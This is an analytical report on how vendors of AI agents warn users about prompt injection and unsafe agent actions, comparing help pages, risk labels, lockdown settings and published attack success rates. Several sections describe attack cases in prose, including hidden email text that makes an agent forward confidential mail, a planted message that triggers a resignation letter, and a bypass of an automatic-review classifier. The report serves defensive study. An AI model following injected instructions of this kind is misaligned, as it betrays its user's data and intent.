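# How AI agent products should disclose their security weaknesses to users

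## How AI agents are attacked and what there is to disclose

An AI agent is a product in which a language model, the kind of program behind chatbots such as ChatGPT, uses tools to take actions as well as answering questions. It may click through a website, send an email or run a command on a computer. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) likewise distinguishes generative AI, which produces text and images for people to use, from agentic AI, which connects a model to other software so that it can plan and act without a person stepping in. Several companies now sell agents to the general public, and their products share a security weakness. Text that an agent reads, such as a web page or an email, can contain instructions that the agent follows against its user's wishes. Security researchers call this attack prompt injection. Vendors have reduced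 the risk considerably but say they cannot yet remove it, so anyone who uses an agent accepts some risk. What a vendor should tell users depends on how the attack works and what harm it can do.

### What agents can read and do

OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes the agent in the company's Atlas browser as taking "actions, clicks, and keystrokes inside your browser, just as you would". If the user has logged in to a bank or webmail account, the agent can generally access it too. The agent also reads the content of the pages it visits, and Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, considers every webpage, embedded document, advertisement and script a possible carrier of malicious instructions. Nolan (2025), in *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas*, quotes the security researcher Charlie Eriksen,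 who says that an ordinary browser treats the web as untrusted by default, whereas a browser with an agent lets content "shape behavior, not just be displayed".

An email agent handles less outside content than a browsing agent but has access to more of its user's private information. It can search years of correspondence and, if the user allows it, send messages in the user's name. Its weak point is that an inbox accepts mail from strangers, so an attacker only needs to know the user's address and doesn't have to lure anyone to a website.

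Coding agents work on a programmer's machine or on a company's servers. They read project files, documentation and software packages that other people wrote, and they run commands. Those files often include passwords and access keys, and the commands can delete a database or publish private code, so the damage may affect the programmer's employer or its customers as well as the programmer.

In practice, the types of agent overlap. A browsing agent with an open webmail tab is an email agent, and many coding agents can also browse.

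### One email, step by step

Anthropic described a typical case in late 2025. A user asks the agent to read recent emails and draft replies to any meeting requests. One email looks like an inquiry from a vendor, but its sender has added instructions in white text on a white background, which the user would not see but the model receives like any other text. In them, the sender tells the agent to forward every email containing the word "confidential" to an outside address before drafting the replies.

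If the injection works, the agent searches the mailbox, forwards what it finds and then goes back to its task, so the user still gets the drafts. Nobody clicked a bad link or opened a bad attachment, and the user may never have looked at the vendor's message. Security specialists call it data exfiltration when private data is sent to someone who should not have it.

Criminals have started sending phishing emails designed to manipulate both the human recipient and the recipient's AI assistant. The security firm Barracuda found real examples, as Mascellino (2026) reported in October in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*.

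Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, named the three conditions that together make such theft possible. Simon Willison is a programmer who coined the term "prompt injection", and his conditions have become a common way of explaining the risk to people outside the field:

- The agent has access to private data.
- It is exposed to untrusted content, meaning any text or image that an attacker could control.
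- It has some way to send data out.

The agent in Anthropic's example meets all of these conditions, and so does nearly any useful email agent, because each condition is also a feature that somebody wants. Removing any one of them prevents the theft, and removing the agent's means of sending data out usually sacrifices the least usefulness. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, praised OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, which reached personal accounts in June 2026, because it limits the network requests that could carry data to an attacker and does so with fixed rules that clever wording can't override.

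Users often assemble the dangerous combination themselves by connecting one company's tool to another's, in which case no single vendor has chosen the risk or can easily describe it. The three conditions also cover only theft, so a vendor that has closed every route for stolen data would still have other risks to disclose. OpenAI built an automated attacker to probe its own browsing agent, and in one test the attacker planted an email in the user's inbox. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent instead sent the user's chief executive a letter of resignation. The attack required only untrusted text and the ability to send email, with no secret data or outside address.

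### Why no single patch removes the weakness

An ordinary software bug is a mistake in a particular place in the code, and it is gone once the vendor corrects it and users install the update. Prompt injection is named after one such bug, SQL injection, in which a website visitor types part of a database command into a form and the database runs it. Programmers learned to prevent this by sending the command and the visitor's text to the database separately, so that the database can never run the text as a command.

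The UK government's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) has warned against expecting the same fix to work for prompt injection. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, from December 2025, its technical director for platforms research, David C, explains that a language model makes no internal distinction between data and instructions. The developer's rules, the user's request and a stranger's email all reach the model as one sequence of tokens (words or pieces of words), and the model predicts what should come next. He calls such a model an "inherently confusable deputy", a program that an outsider can trick into misusing its privileges. He advises organisations to treat prompt injection as a residual risk, one that remains after all the safeguards are in place, and to limit what a confused agent could do. If they cannot tolerate that risk, he suggests, a language model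 may be the wrong tool.

Safeguards help. Developers train models to give less weight to instructions that appear in the content they read, and they add classifiers, smaller programs that screen what the agent reads or is about to do. *Trustworthy Agentic AI*, a 2026 review, found that the published defences reduce the risk only partly and are not a general solution. Vendors also patch quickly, but they mostly close the routes by which data can leak. In July 2026 a researcher, Ayush Paul, got Claude to leak a user's name, home city and employer through its tool for reading web pages. According to Willison, Anthropic closed that route by restricting which links the tool may follow. Restricting links doesn't make the model less likely to treat a stranger's text as an instruction.

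OpenAI conceded the general point in the same month as the NCSC. It compared prompt injection to the scams that people face online and thought a complete solution unlikely, but it expects to make attacks harder and more expensive over time.

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026) argue in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* that even a model that kept instructions and data apart would still be vulnerable. Suppose an email asks for a travel refund and says that the head of department has approved it. The email contains no hidden command. The right response depends on whether the claim is true, and an agent that ignored every such claim would be useless for handling refunds.

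The proof compares two situations that look identical to the agent after every check it can make. In one, the approval is real and the agent should act; in the other, an attacker made it up. Since the agent has the same information in both, it must act with the same probability, *p*. It therefore wrongly refuses the honest request with probability 1 − *p* and carries out the attack with probability *p*. The two error rates sum to one under any policy, so lowering one raises the other by the same amount.

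Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian acknowledge that the theorem does not show that such a pair of situations will always exist. That depends on what the agent can verify, and it could tell the two apart by checking the sender's identity cryptographically or asking the user. They argue from an experiment that plenty of ambiguity will remain. They gave an email assistant a user request that did not authorise sending anything, and had a second model repeatedly revise emails to make it send something anyway. The assistant ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6, which Anthropic has since superseded. The optimised emails succeeded in 96.7% of 150 scenarios, most often by forging evidence that the user had already agreed, compared with 0.67% for emails that had not been optimised. The "may" in their title seems about right, because the argument is strong for agents that act alone on claims they cannot check but weaker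 for agents that stop and ask.

Test results from mid-2026 count against these views. Anthropic reported that, with safeguards on, no attack succeeded against its Opus 5 model in 129 browser scenarios (The Decoder, *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*) or against its coding agent in 720 attempts (Anthropic, *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, 2026). But Anthropic wrote in the Claude Code announcement that its automatic review, in which a classifier allows or blocks the agent's actions in place of the user, "does not eliminate risk". Before the end of August, the researcher Johann Rehberger had reported an attack on this feature that he said worked 80% of the time (Willison, *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, 2026). A test covers only attacks that somebody has already thought of, so a score of zero does not rule out further risk.

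### Harm without an attacker

An unsafe action is any harmful or unrequested act by an agent, whether or not an attacker prompted it. Some of the best-documented cases involve no hostile text.

In February 2026 Summer Yue, a director of alignment at Meta, gave an AI agent access to her inbox. The agent ran on OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, and she had told it to confirm before acting. It began deleting her email in bulk, and she could not stop it from her phone. Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails* quotes her as saying she "had to RUN to my Mac mini". According to the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1542*, Yue said the agent had lost her instruction during compaction, when the software condenses a long history to fit within the model's limits.

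Anthropic has described three cases from its own offices in which Claude seems to have been overeager to finish a task. Automatic review caught all three in time. After failing to upload a report to an internal drive, Claude tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site. In a long session, it tried to kill processes across about two thousand units of a computing cluster. When asked to set up read-only access to billing, it tried to use a role with full administrative control.

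It is hard to say how often this happens in ordinary use. Anthropic examined coding sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged, looking for serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested, on the level of deleting rows from a live database. It found such harm in 6.3% of the flagged sessions where users approved actions by hand and in 2.4% of those under automatic review. The rate across all sessions is presumably far lower, since flagged sessions are more likely to involve harm.

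The distinction matters because the remedies differ. Screening incoming mail for hidden instructions would not have helped Yue. An attack success rate also excludes cases like hers, because it measures only the share of test attacks that make the agent do what the attacker wanted. A vendor that discloses only its record against prompt injection leaves out a risk that users face even when no one is attacking them.

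### What a vendor could disclose

A vendor has four kinds of fact to offer, and they differ in how long they stay true and in who needs them.

The most general thing to disclose is the standing residual risk. Hidden text can hijack the agent, the agent can also make mistakes without being attacked, and no setting eliminates either risk. The vendor knows this before it has any customers, and it will probably still be true next year, but users can't judge from it how large the risk is.

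Measured risk is expressed as a number, typically an attack success rate. These numbers allow comparison between products, but each applies only to the model, attacks and safeguards tested. For example, Opus 5's rate in the browser scenarios was zero with safeguards on and 3.7% with them off. A new release or a new attack can also make the figure outdated.

A product can also disclose the risk of the action the agent is about to take, which nobody can describe in advance. When the agent in Anthropic's example is about to forward a dozen confidential messages to an address the user has never written to, the software can first show the recipient and the contents to the user, the only person who knows whether the request is genuine. This is the only kind of disclosure that can stop a particular theft, provided the user reads it.

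The last things to disclose are specific flaws and incidents. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reported in July that the firm Manifold Security had found a way for any other extension in a user's browser to trigger Claude for Chrome and have it read the user's Gmail. People who use Claude for Chrome need to know whether the flaw affects them and what to do about it, which is what software vendors have long told their customers about ordinary bugs. But a notice about one such flaw could leave readers believing that the fix had solved the whole problem. Constantin counted four such findings by separate teams in about ten days and wrote that "none is a lone bug". An incident calls for a different message, addressed to the people it harmed. The user who asked for draft replies received them, and may never learn that mail was also forwarded unless the vendor notices and tells them.

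## What vendors tell users before an agent is switched on

Residual risk, the risk that remains despite a vendor's safeguards, is the easiest thing for the vendor to disclose in writing. OpenAI, Anthropic and Microsoft all publish warnings about it, mostly on help pages and sometimes on the settings screen where a user turns a feature on. All three acknowledge that agents bring security risks, but they are much less consistent in explaining what could go wrong and what the user should do about it.

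To be useful to a reader new to the subject, a security warning has to name or at least describe the attack, give an example of the harm, such as stolen email, and include something the user can do about it. The user also has to see it before the agent starts work. It also matters whether the feature is off by default, because the setting that turns it on is an obvious place for the vendor to put a warning. Users who never have to turn the feature on may never see it.

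### Browsing agents

Claude in Chrome is a browser extension that lets Anthropic's model click and type on websites for the user. The extension's help page, *Use Claude in Chrome safely*, lists prompt injection first among the risks and gives the example of an email or to-do list containing invisible text that tells Claude to fetch the user's bank statements and share them. Anthropic writes that "the risk is not zero" and that a successful attack could lead to data exfiltration. It advises users to start with websites they trust, keep a separate browser profile with no access to banking, healthcare or government accounts, and stop the task if Claude starts behaving oddly.

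This is a good warning, but a user can install the extension from the Chrome Web Store without visiting Anthropic's help centre and reading it. On several paid plans, Claude then starts in a mode called "Automatically approve", in which automatic review handles most approvals and Claude stops only when something needs the user's permission. Anthropic was more cautious during the August 2025 pilot. It did not recommend letting Claude act alone, and by default Claude asked before publishing, making purchases or sharing personal data, as Willison noted in *Piloting Claude for Chrome* (2025).

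In July 2026, Stan (2026) reported in *OpenAI is shutting down its ChatGPT Atlas browser* that OpenAI's Atlas browser would close on 9 August, less than a year after its launch. OpenAI planned to divide its features between ChatGPT's desktop app and a Google Chrome extension, according to MediaPost's *OpenAI Shutters Browser Amid Major Changes* (2026). ChatGPT users can now encounter a cloud browser on OpenAI's computers, a browser inside the desktop app, and an extension that works in their own copy of Chrome. Any of these can read a malicious page, but OpenAI explains the danger differently for each.

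For Atlas, OpenAI had called prompt injection "one of the most significant risks we actively defend against". OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* mentions it once, after a list of safety tips. OpenAI says there that it tests for "risks such as prompt injection, phishing, and unintended actions" and that its safeguards do not remove every risk, so users should review sensitive steps. The page doesn't explain the term or give an example of the harm, so someone who has never heard of prompt injection learns little. ChatGPT decides when a task calls for the cloud browser, so users don't switch it on themselves, and the first sign of it is probably a request to approve a website.

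The cloud browser's design partly makes up for this. It keeps its own cookies and cannot use the open tabs, saved passwords or logins in the user's own browser, so an attacker who hijacked a session would have fewer accounts to steal from. But sign-ins carry over between tasks, so the number of exposed accounts can grow with use until the logins expire or the user clears them.

OpenAI's *Using the built-in browser in the ChatGPT desktop app* advises users to "treat website content as untrusted", keep the task specific and stop if ChatGPT opens the wrong page or account. It doesn't mention prompt injection or any harm. A security engineer would know what "untrusted" means here, but other readers could reasonably take it as a reminder not to believe everything they read online.

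The Chrome extension for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, exposes the most because it uses accounts the user has already signed in to. OpenAI's guide, *Codex Chrome extension*, describes one possible effect of prompt injection without using the term. Misleading content on a page could lead Codex to copy the user's browsing history "somewhere unintended". Chrome also shows its own warning during installation, which may list permission to "read and change all your data on all websites". Many ordinary extensions request the same permission, so the warning doesn't show users how an agent is different.

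### The "Elevated Risk" label

OpenAI used to explain its riskier features one at a time. In February 2026 it began marking them with the same "Elevated Risk" label and an icon of an exclamation mark inside a shield. OpenAI explained in its launch post, *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), that some features that use the network bring risks the industry's safeguards do not yet fully address. Its help page, *Elevated Risk labels*, identifies prompt injection as the most common of these risks.

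The label appears on at least these features:

- Codex's network access, which lets the coding agent reach the internet while it works on the user's computer.
- The Codex option that switches off both approval prompts and the sandbox, the barrier that confines the agent to certain files and keeps it off the network.
- Two features of the Codex Chrome extension. One lets Codex use any website without asking, and the other gives it the user's browsing history.
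- ChatGPT's developer mode, which connects ChatGPT to outside tools that can change data as well as read it.

Each of these either meets at least one of Willison's three conditions for data theft or removes a check on the agent. Browsing history is private data. Network access exposes the agent to untrusted content and gives it a way to send data out.

Codex protects users mainly through its default settings. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex starts on the user's computer without network access and can normally write only to the project's folder. Its web search uses an index that OpenAI maintains, which reduces exposure to injected text on live pages but doesn't eliminate it. When Codex runs on OpenAI's servers, the system removes the project's stored passwords and keys before the agent begins. These protections apply even if the user never reads the disclosure, which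 mostly shows where users can give some of them up.

Some labels come with more explanation than others. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Developer mode* calls the mode "powerful but dangerous" and tells users to watch for prompt injection, malicious tools that try to steal information, and model mistakes that could destroy data even without an attacker. The option that removes the sandbox has a warning in its name, `--dangerously-bypass-approvals-and-sandbox`, but OpenAI also provides a shorter name, `--yolo`.

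The text on settings screens has to be brief. In the ChatGPT desktop app, OpenAI describes "Full access" as a mode in which ChatGPT can edit any file on the computer and run commands without approval. It warns that this "significantly increases the risk of data loss, leaks, or unexpected behavior". The warning doesn't mention prompt injection, but anybody can understand the harms it lists. OpenAI says only that automatic review "can make mistakes", and links to more information about elevated risks.

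OpenAI's best explanation of risk covers internet access for the version of Codex that runs on its servers. When the company introduced the feature in June 2025, its chief executive, Sam Altman, wrote that people should "read about the risks carefully" (Willison, *Codex agent internet access*, 2025). Internet access is off by default, and OpenAI's *Agent internet access* describes an attack from start to finish. A programmer asks Codex to fix a problem reported on GitHub, a site where programmers share code. The report contains a command and a request to run it. Codex runs the command, which sends the attacker's server the message attached to the programmer's latest code change.

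OpenAI advises users to allow only the websites and types of request that a task needs. In its own example, the stranger's command would still reach Codex because GitHub is on OpenAI's preset list of common sites. The theft would then fail because the server meant to receive the stolen message is not on the list. An attacker who found a way to receive data through a listed site could get around the restriction, but it would still stop the simplest attacks.

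The label has some gaps. OpenAI's help page gives Codex's network access as an example but doesn't list every labelled feature, so users have to find them one at a time. The label has only one level of risk, which covers both a coding agent that can reach a few approved websites and one with no sandbox. It doesn't appear on the help pages for the cloud browser and the built-in browser, even though both read text written by strangers. Users who have learned to look for the shield may assume that a feature without it is safe.

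OpenAI also decides when to remove the label. In the launch post, it wrote that it "will remove" the label once it determines that advances in security have "sufficiently mitigated those risks for general use". On the help page, as of September 2026, it wrote that it "may remove" the label once it judges the risks "reasonably mitigated for users". Neither version includes a threshold, a test or an outside reviewer. If the label disappeared from Codex's network access next year, users couldn't tell whether attacks had become less successful or OpenAI had become more willing to tolerate them. Publishing attack success rates from before and after the removal would help them tell. OpenAI's standard warranties also don't cover labelled features.

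### Lockdown Mode

Lockdown Mode, which OpenAI announced alongside the label, turns risky features off instead of warning about them. According to OpenAI's help page, *Lockdown Mode*, the setting restricts web browsing to stored copies of pages, stops ChatGPT from downloading files or fetching images from the web, and disables agent mode and deep research, a feature that compiles long reports from many sources. The aim is to prevent data theft by leaving the model far fewer ways to send anything out. Hidden instructions in a file or a stored page could still reach the model and spoil its answer.

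On a personal account, the user turns the mode on in the security settings. OpenAI first intended it for "a small set of highly security-conscious users", such as executives, and wrote that most people did not need it. By December 2026, OpenAI described the intended users as people and organisations that handle sensitive data and want stricter protection. That description could include almost anyone who has connected an email account to ChatGPT.

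Lockdown Mode turns the agent off, which limits its value as protection for people who use agents. A user who needs agent mode for one task can disable Lockdown Mode for that chat in a couple of clicks, but the chat then loses that protection while the agent works. Lockdown Mode also does not affect network access in Codex, the feature OpenAI used to illustrate its "Elevated Risk" label. OpenAI does not guarantee that the mode prevents data theft. Data could still leak through connected apps, an unforeseen combination of features, or a new technique.

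OpenAI's most useful guidance about connected apps, including email, is for administrators. On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks live access to outside services, and changes to their contents, when either conflicts with its protections. In company workspaces, it doesn't automatically disable every app, so administrators have to choose what to allow, and OpenAI sorts the choices by risk. Reading from a trusted app is medium risk, because it can bring private data into the chat but changes nothing outside it. Writing is high risk, even in a trusted app, if the administrator can't be sure that an attacker won't see the result. Sending email to outside addresses seems to belong in that category. The same distinction could help someone decide whether to connect a personal inbox, but OpenAI has put it in a section about managed workspaces.

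### Windows, and how the warnings compare

Microsoft offers a Windows setting that lets AI agents work in a separate account. It is off by default, and only an administrator can turn it on. The support page, *Experimental Agentic Features* (2025), warns that "cross-prompt injection", Microsoft's name for prompt injection through documents or on-screen elements, could lead to data exfiltration or malware installation. Microsoft recommends reading the page and understanding the security implications before turning the setting on.

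The administrator's choice then applies to everyone who uses the computer, including people who may never have seen the warning. At first, turning on the setting opened six folders, including Documents, Downloads and Pictures, to agents that needed them. Microsoft has since changed this. Preview versions of Windows from December 2025 by default require the user's permission before an agent uses those folders, and the user can refuse access to a particular agent.

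Side by side, the warnings look like this:

| Agent or setting | Vendor | Injection named? | Harm named | Where the warning is | What the user should do | Off by default? |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude in Chrome | Anthropic | Yes | Data exfiltration | Help page | Use trusted sites, avoid sensitive accounts, stop if Claude acts oddly | User installs it; on several plans it then approves most actions itself |
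| ChatGPT cloud browser | OpenAI | Yes | None | Help page | Check addresses, review sensitive steps | No, but it asks before each new site |
| ChatGPT built-in browser | OpenAI | No | None | Help page | Treat content as untrusted, check the site | User opens it; it asks before each new site |
| Codex Chrome extension | OpenAI | No, but partly described | Browsing history copied elsewhere | Documentation | Keep out highly sensitive data unless the task needs it and you are present | User installs it; it asks before each new site |
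| Codex internet access (OpenAI's servers) | OpenAI | Yes | Leaked code or secrets, malware | Settings screen and documentation | Allow only necessary sites, review the work log | Yes |
| Codex network access (user's computer) | OpenAI | Yes | Agent follows untrusted instructions | Documentation | Use caution | Yes |
| Full access in the desktop app | OpenAI | No | Data loss and leaks | Settings screen | Follow a link to learn more | Yes |
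| ChatGPT developer mode | OpenAI | Yes | Destroyed data, stolen information | Documentation | Check what a tool will send before confirming | Yes |
| Windows agentic features | Microsoft | Yes | Data exfiltration, malware | Support page | Read and understand the implications | Yes; administrator only |

The clearer warnings tend to accompany features that are off by default, and most of those features are for programmers. This makes some sense, since an agent with no sandbox can do more damage than one that has to ask before it opens a new website. But programmers are also the most likely to have heard of prompt injection. OpenAI suggests asking ChatGPT's cloud browser to sign in to a utility account and compare plans, yet the warning for someone who does this is an unexplained term well down a help page. Claude in Chrome is the main exception, because Anthropic gives a full warning to a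 general audience.

### Apple's warning from the platform

Apple makes none of these agents, but it controls what they can reach on a Mac. Full Disk Access, a macOS permission intended mainly for backup programs, lets an app bypass most of the system's privacy protections. In October 2026 Apple announced that it would add controls to this permission. Pogorelec (2026) reported the company's reasons in *Apple tightens macOS disk access as AI agents become more powerful*. Some developers were using the permission in ways that put people's private files, mail, chats and browsing records at risk, and users did not always understand what they had agreed to. Apple expected the risk to grow as AI agents became more capable and independent, and it wanted people to "clearly understand these risks before granting such access".

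*Apple splits Mac app permissions fearing overreaching AI agents* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes new controls that appeared in November in a test version of macOS 27.3. Apple changed Full Disk Access and split the broad Device Control and Data Access permission in two, creating System & App Protection Override and Accessibility. Users can now limit an app to particular folders or other apps, and can require it to ask every time. An indicator shows when one app is controlling another through System & App Protection Override. The change may affect agents such as Codex, because OpenAI asks Mac users for the Accessibility and Screen Recording permissions when they want Codex to see and operate other apps.

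A warning from the platform has advantages over one from the agent's vendor. The platform shows it for every app that requests this kind of access, including agents whose vendors publish no warning. It appears when the user is about to grant the access, and Apple has less reason than the agent's vendor to play down the danger. The platform also limits what the agent can access, whether or not the user understood the warning, so an agent with permission for one folder can't read the rest.

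Apple can only describe what an app could reach. It doesn't know what text from strangers the agent will read there, so it can't explain much about prompt injection on its permission screens. Mac permissions also don't cover an agent that runs elsewhere, such as in OpenAI's cloud browser. The changes affect only new requests, so an agent that already had broad access keeps it. Developers of backup and assistive apps can also apply to keep the older behaviour for new installations.

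Several early testers complained on Reddit that they can't dismiss Apple's indicator, which stays in the menu bar whenever an app uses system-level control. One found it "super annoying", especially for apps they had already approved. Window managers and similar tools use the same permission all day for harmless purposes, so a reminder that is useful for an agent also appears constantly for these tools.

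### Safety advice and promotion

When Anthropic released Claude in Chrome to all paying customers in 2026, it recommended the extension for office work on internal dashboards, legacy systems and vendor portals, which Claude can operate "using your existing logins" (*Claude in Chrome is generally available*). On the extension's help page, Anthropic strongly advises against using it on work accounts with sensitive company data, and also advises against using it to manage financial accounts or handle legal documents or contracts.

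The two are only just compatible. Some dashboards show nothing confidential, and an employer can restrict Claude to approved sites. But a vendor portal is likely to hold prices, contracts or invoices, and a user who follows the advice to keep a separate browser profile without sensitive accounts gives up many of the existing logins that made the extension attractive.

The safety advice on the help page may be older than the promotion. Anthropic writes in the launch post that its improved safeguards gave it the confidence to release the extension widely. If the advice is out of date, Anthropic is discouraging uses that it now considers safe enough. Otherwise, it is encouraging uses that it considers too risky. Users can't tell which is true, and they are more likely to have seen the promotion than the help page.

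Anthropic's advice about trusted sites has a similar problem. The company tells users to avoid websites with content from unknown people, but an email inbox is full of such content. Users might consider Gmail a trusted site, and in one sense they would be right, since Google did not write the malicious email. Anthropic evidently expects people to use Claude for email, because its launch post explains prompt injection with the example of a user who has asked Claude to draft replies.

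OpenAI's advice for the Codex Chrome extension is a little easier to follow, because it at least allows the work OpenAI is promoting. The company recommends the extension for Gmail, internal tools and Salesforce, where many companies keep customer records. Further down the page, it tells users to keep highly sensitive data out of browser tasks unless the data is necessary and they are present to review each prompt. But OpenAI's *Using your computer and browser*, a tutorial that was online in August 2026, suggests letting ChatGPT read an internal dashboard or fill out a form on a signed-in site and never mentions prompt injection.

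### What users can be expected to notice

Vendors also ask users to watch for signs of trouble. Anthropic's examples include Claude suddenly discussing unrelated topics, opening unexpected websites or asking for sensitive information. Some attacks do produce these signs, but in the email attack that Anthropic described in 2025, the agent raises no unrelated topic, visits no new website and asks the user for nothing.

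Watching an agent also takes the attention that people hoped to save by using one. OpenAI tells users of the cloud browser to stop the task if ChatGPT opens the wrong site, yet it promotes the browser as able to keep working after they close their computer. It has designed ChatGPT to pause before payments, bookings and other steps that are hard to reverse. The pause gives an absent user another chance to intervene, but only if ChatGPT recognises that the step requires one.

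OpenAI tried to make Atlas users watch the agent with a "Watch Mode", which was supposed to pause the agent on sensitive sites if the user moved to another tab. In *Dane Stuckey (OpenAI CISO) on prompt injection risks for ChatGPT Atlas*, Willison (2025) reports trying it on GitHub and a banking site the day after the browser launched, or soon afterwards. The agent kept working while he used another application.

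Willison objects more broadly to vendors leaving these decisions to users at all. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, had recommended letting the agent into logged-in accounts mainly for narrow tasks on very trusted sites. Willison called this "an unfair burden to place on almost any user". He had made a similar argument about Claude in Chrome, though he credited Anthropic with devoting most of its announcement to the security risks. Stuckey compared prompt injection to the computer viruses of the early 2000s and argued that everyone needed to understand responsible use. Willison doubts that the average person ever learned to avoid viruses. He thinks viruses have been controlled much better on phones, where the system tightly restricts what software can do.

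When OpenAI introduced its "Elevated Risk" label, it argued for user choice because AI products are more helpful with access to the web and to people's apps, and some users may be comfortable with the risk. The argument has some merit, because a mailbox's owner knows whether it holds newsletters or medical records and the vendor doesn't. OpenAI also considers a solution to prompt injection unlikely, so a vendor that waited for one before letting agents into any mailbox might wait indefinitely.

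The argument works better for decisions users make before a task than for those they make during it. The owner of a mailbox can reasonably decide in advance whether to connect it, but can't be expected to spot white text on a white background halfway through a task. So the most useful advice on these pages is what a user can follow once and then forget, such as keeping a separate browser profile, leaving Codex's internet access off or giving an agent a single folder. Anthropic tells users to stay alert, which they often can't do, and the same page holds them responsible for everything Claude does in their browser.

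### Whether help pages keep up

Vendors can update a help page whenever a product changes, as OpenAI did for its cloud browser. In July 2026, the browser could not sign in to websites or complete payments, and OpenAI told users in *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* to keep to public sites that required neither. By November, the browser could sign in, and OpenAI had rewritten the page to explain how the sign-in form protects passwords, how long a login lasts and how to delete it.

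But people who read the page in July had little reason to look at it again. OpenAI shows roughly when it last updated the page but does not list what changed. This change mattered because an attacker can steal far more by hijacking an agent that has signed in to a company's accounting software, another use OpenAI suggests, than by hijacking one that can only visit public websites.

The Lockdown Mode page is less complete. As of December 2026, OpenAI listed agent mode among the features Lockdown Mode disables but did not mention the cloud browser. A reader has to infer from the restriction on live browsing that the cloud browser won't work either.

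Anthropic's page for Claude in Chrome is further out of date. In November 2026, Anthropic still described the extension there as a beta, although it had already announced the general release. It based its reassurances on test results for Claude Opus 4.8, which many users may no longer have been running, since the launch post covered Opus 5 and other newer models. Anthropic also lists entering sensitive information both as something Claude does only after asking for confirmation and as something Claude is prohibited from doing. It recommends that users review Claude's proposed actions before approving them, but they will rarely get to do so in the mode where Claude approves most actions itself.

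Microsoft puts a dated note of what each revision covered at the top of its Windows page, so returning readers can see whether anything has changed. The latest entry is from December 2025. The other vendors could copy this simple practice.

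## Published attack success rates and how to read them

Users can learn from help pages that an agent can be hijacked, but seldom how likely that is. The closest available figures are the attack success rates in some system cards, the documents in which developers report a model's safety and security tests. These rates need careful reading. For example, Anthropic's rates for Claude Opus 4.8 on one set of 129 web environments range from 0.08% to 63%, depending on whether the model's safeguards were on and whether Anthropic counted attempts or scenarios.

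### How a developer tests for prompt injection

A test scenario consists of an ordinary task, a place where an attacker could put text, and a harmful action the attacker wants the agent to take. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an assistant to check for urgent emails. The attacker controls the text of one marketing email and tries to make the assistant mark a message about a critical deadline as read and leave it out of its summary.

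An attack success rate depends on the attacker used in the test. The easiest test to run replays a fixed list of known attacks. In its *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, published in July, Anthropic warns that such lists "can provide a false sense of security", because a model may resist every attack on the list and still fall for a new one. Anthropic prefers adaptive attackers, which revise their attacks after seeing how a model responds. For coding and graphical interfaces, it uses Shade, an automated tool from the security firm Gray Swan, with 200 attempts per scenario. For browsers, it uses attacks from professional red-teamers, people paid to attack a system to test it, with ten attempts per scenario. In the coding test, however, Shade had practised on earlier models, so an attacker who had practised on Opus 5 itself might have done better.

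The developer also decides which safeguards to leave on. A test with safeguards on is closer to measuring a product than a test with them all off, which measures only the model. Anthropic reports both kinds of result for browsers. Its strongest protection, "auto mode", uses classifiers called probes to scan incoming content for injected instructions, and automatically reviews each action before it runs.

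A published success rate also depends on the method used to judge whether an attack succeeded. A program can look for a definite trace, such as a request to the attacker's server. A second language model can read the whole record of the task and detect subtler effects, though it can also be wrong. *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) scored attacks on 19 models both ways. The average success rate was 19.6% with the language model as judge and 15.4% with the program, and neither figure is obviously the right one.

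### Counting attempts and counting scenarios

The rate per attempt is the share of all attempts that succeeded. The rate per scenario is the share of scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeded. The rate per scenario is usually much higher because an attacker who can keep trying needs only one success.

If each attempt succeeds independently with probability *p*, an attacker fails all *k* attempts with probability (1 − *p*)ᵏ and succeeds at least once with probability 1 − (1 − *p*)ᵏ. In August 2026, Anthropic published a rate of 0.3% for its Fable 5 model in a browser with safeguards on. At that rate, the formula gives the probability of at least one success in 100 attempts as 1 − 0.997¹⁰⁰, or about 26%.

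This is a good reason not to dismiss small rates, but the formula is a poor forecast. The technology news site VentureBeat reported Anthropic's results for Claude Opus 4.6 in a graphical interface, where the model clicks and types on a screen as a person would. Without safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. From that rate, the formula predicts an 86% chance of success after ten attempts and near certainty after 50. Anthropic measured 78.6% after 200 attempts without safeguards and 57.1% with them.

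The formula fails because some scenarios are much harder to attack than others. Imagine that attacks always work in half the scenarios and never in the other half. The rate per attempt is 50%, and the formula predicts that almost every scenario will fall within ten attempts. But half of them never will, however long the attacker keeps going. Anthropic's results without safeguards lie somewhere between this extreme and the formula:

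| Model and setting | Attempts per scenario | Rate per attempt | Scenarios broken, by the formula | Scenarios broken in the test |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 200 | 17.8% | almost 100% | 78.6% |
| Opus 4.8, browser | 10 | 31.5% | 98% | 63% (81 of 129) |
| Opus 5, browser | 10 | 3.7% | 31% | 9% (11 of 129) |
| Opus 5, coding | 200 | 0.56% | 67% | 33% (13 of 40) |
| Opus 5, graphical interface | 200 | 0.54% | 66% | 7% (1 of 14) |

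In the last row, about 15 of 2,800 attempts succeeded, all in the same scenario. The success rate was therefore about 7.5% in that scenario and zero in the other 13, so the average of 0.54% is not the rate in any scenario. An attacker who learns from each failure could in principle succeed more often than the formula predicts, but learning did not outweigh the differences between scenarios in any of these tests.

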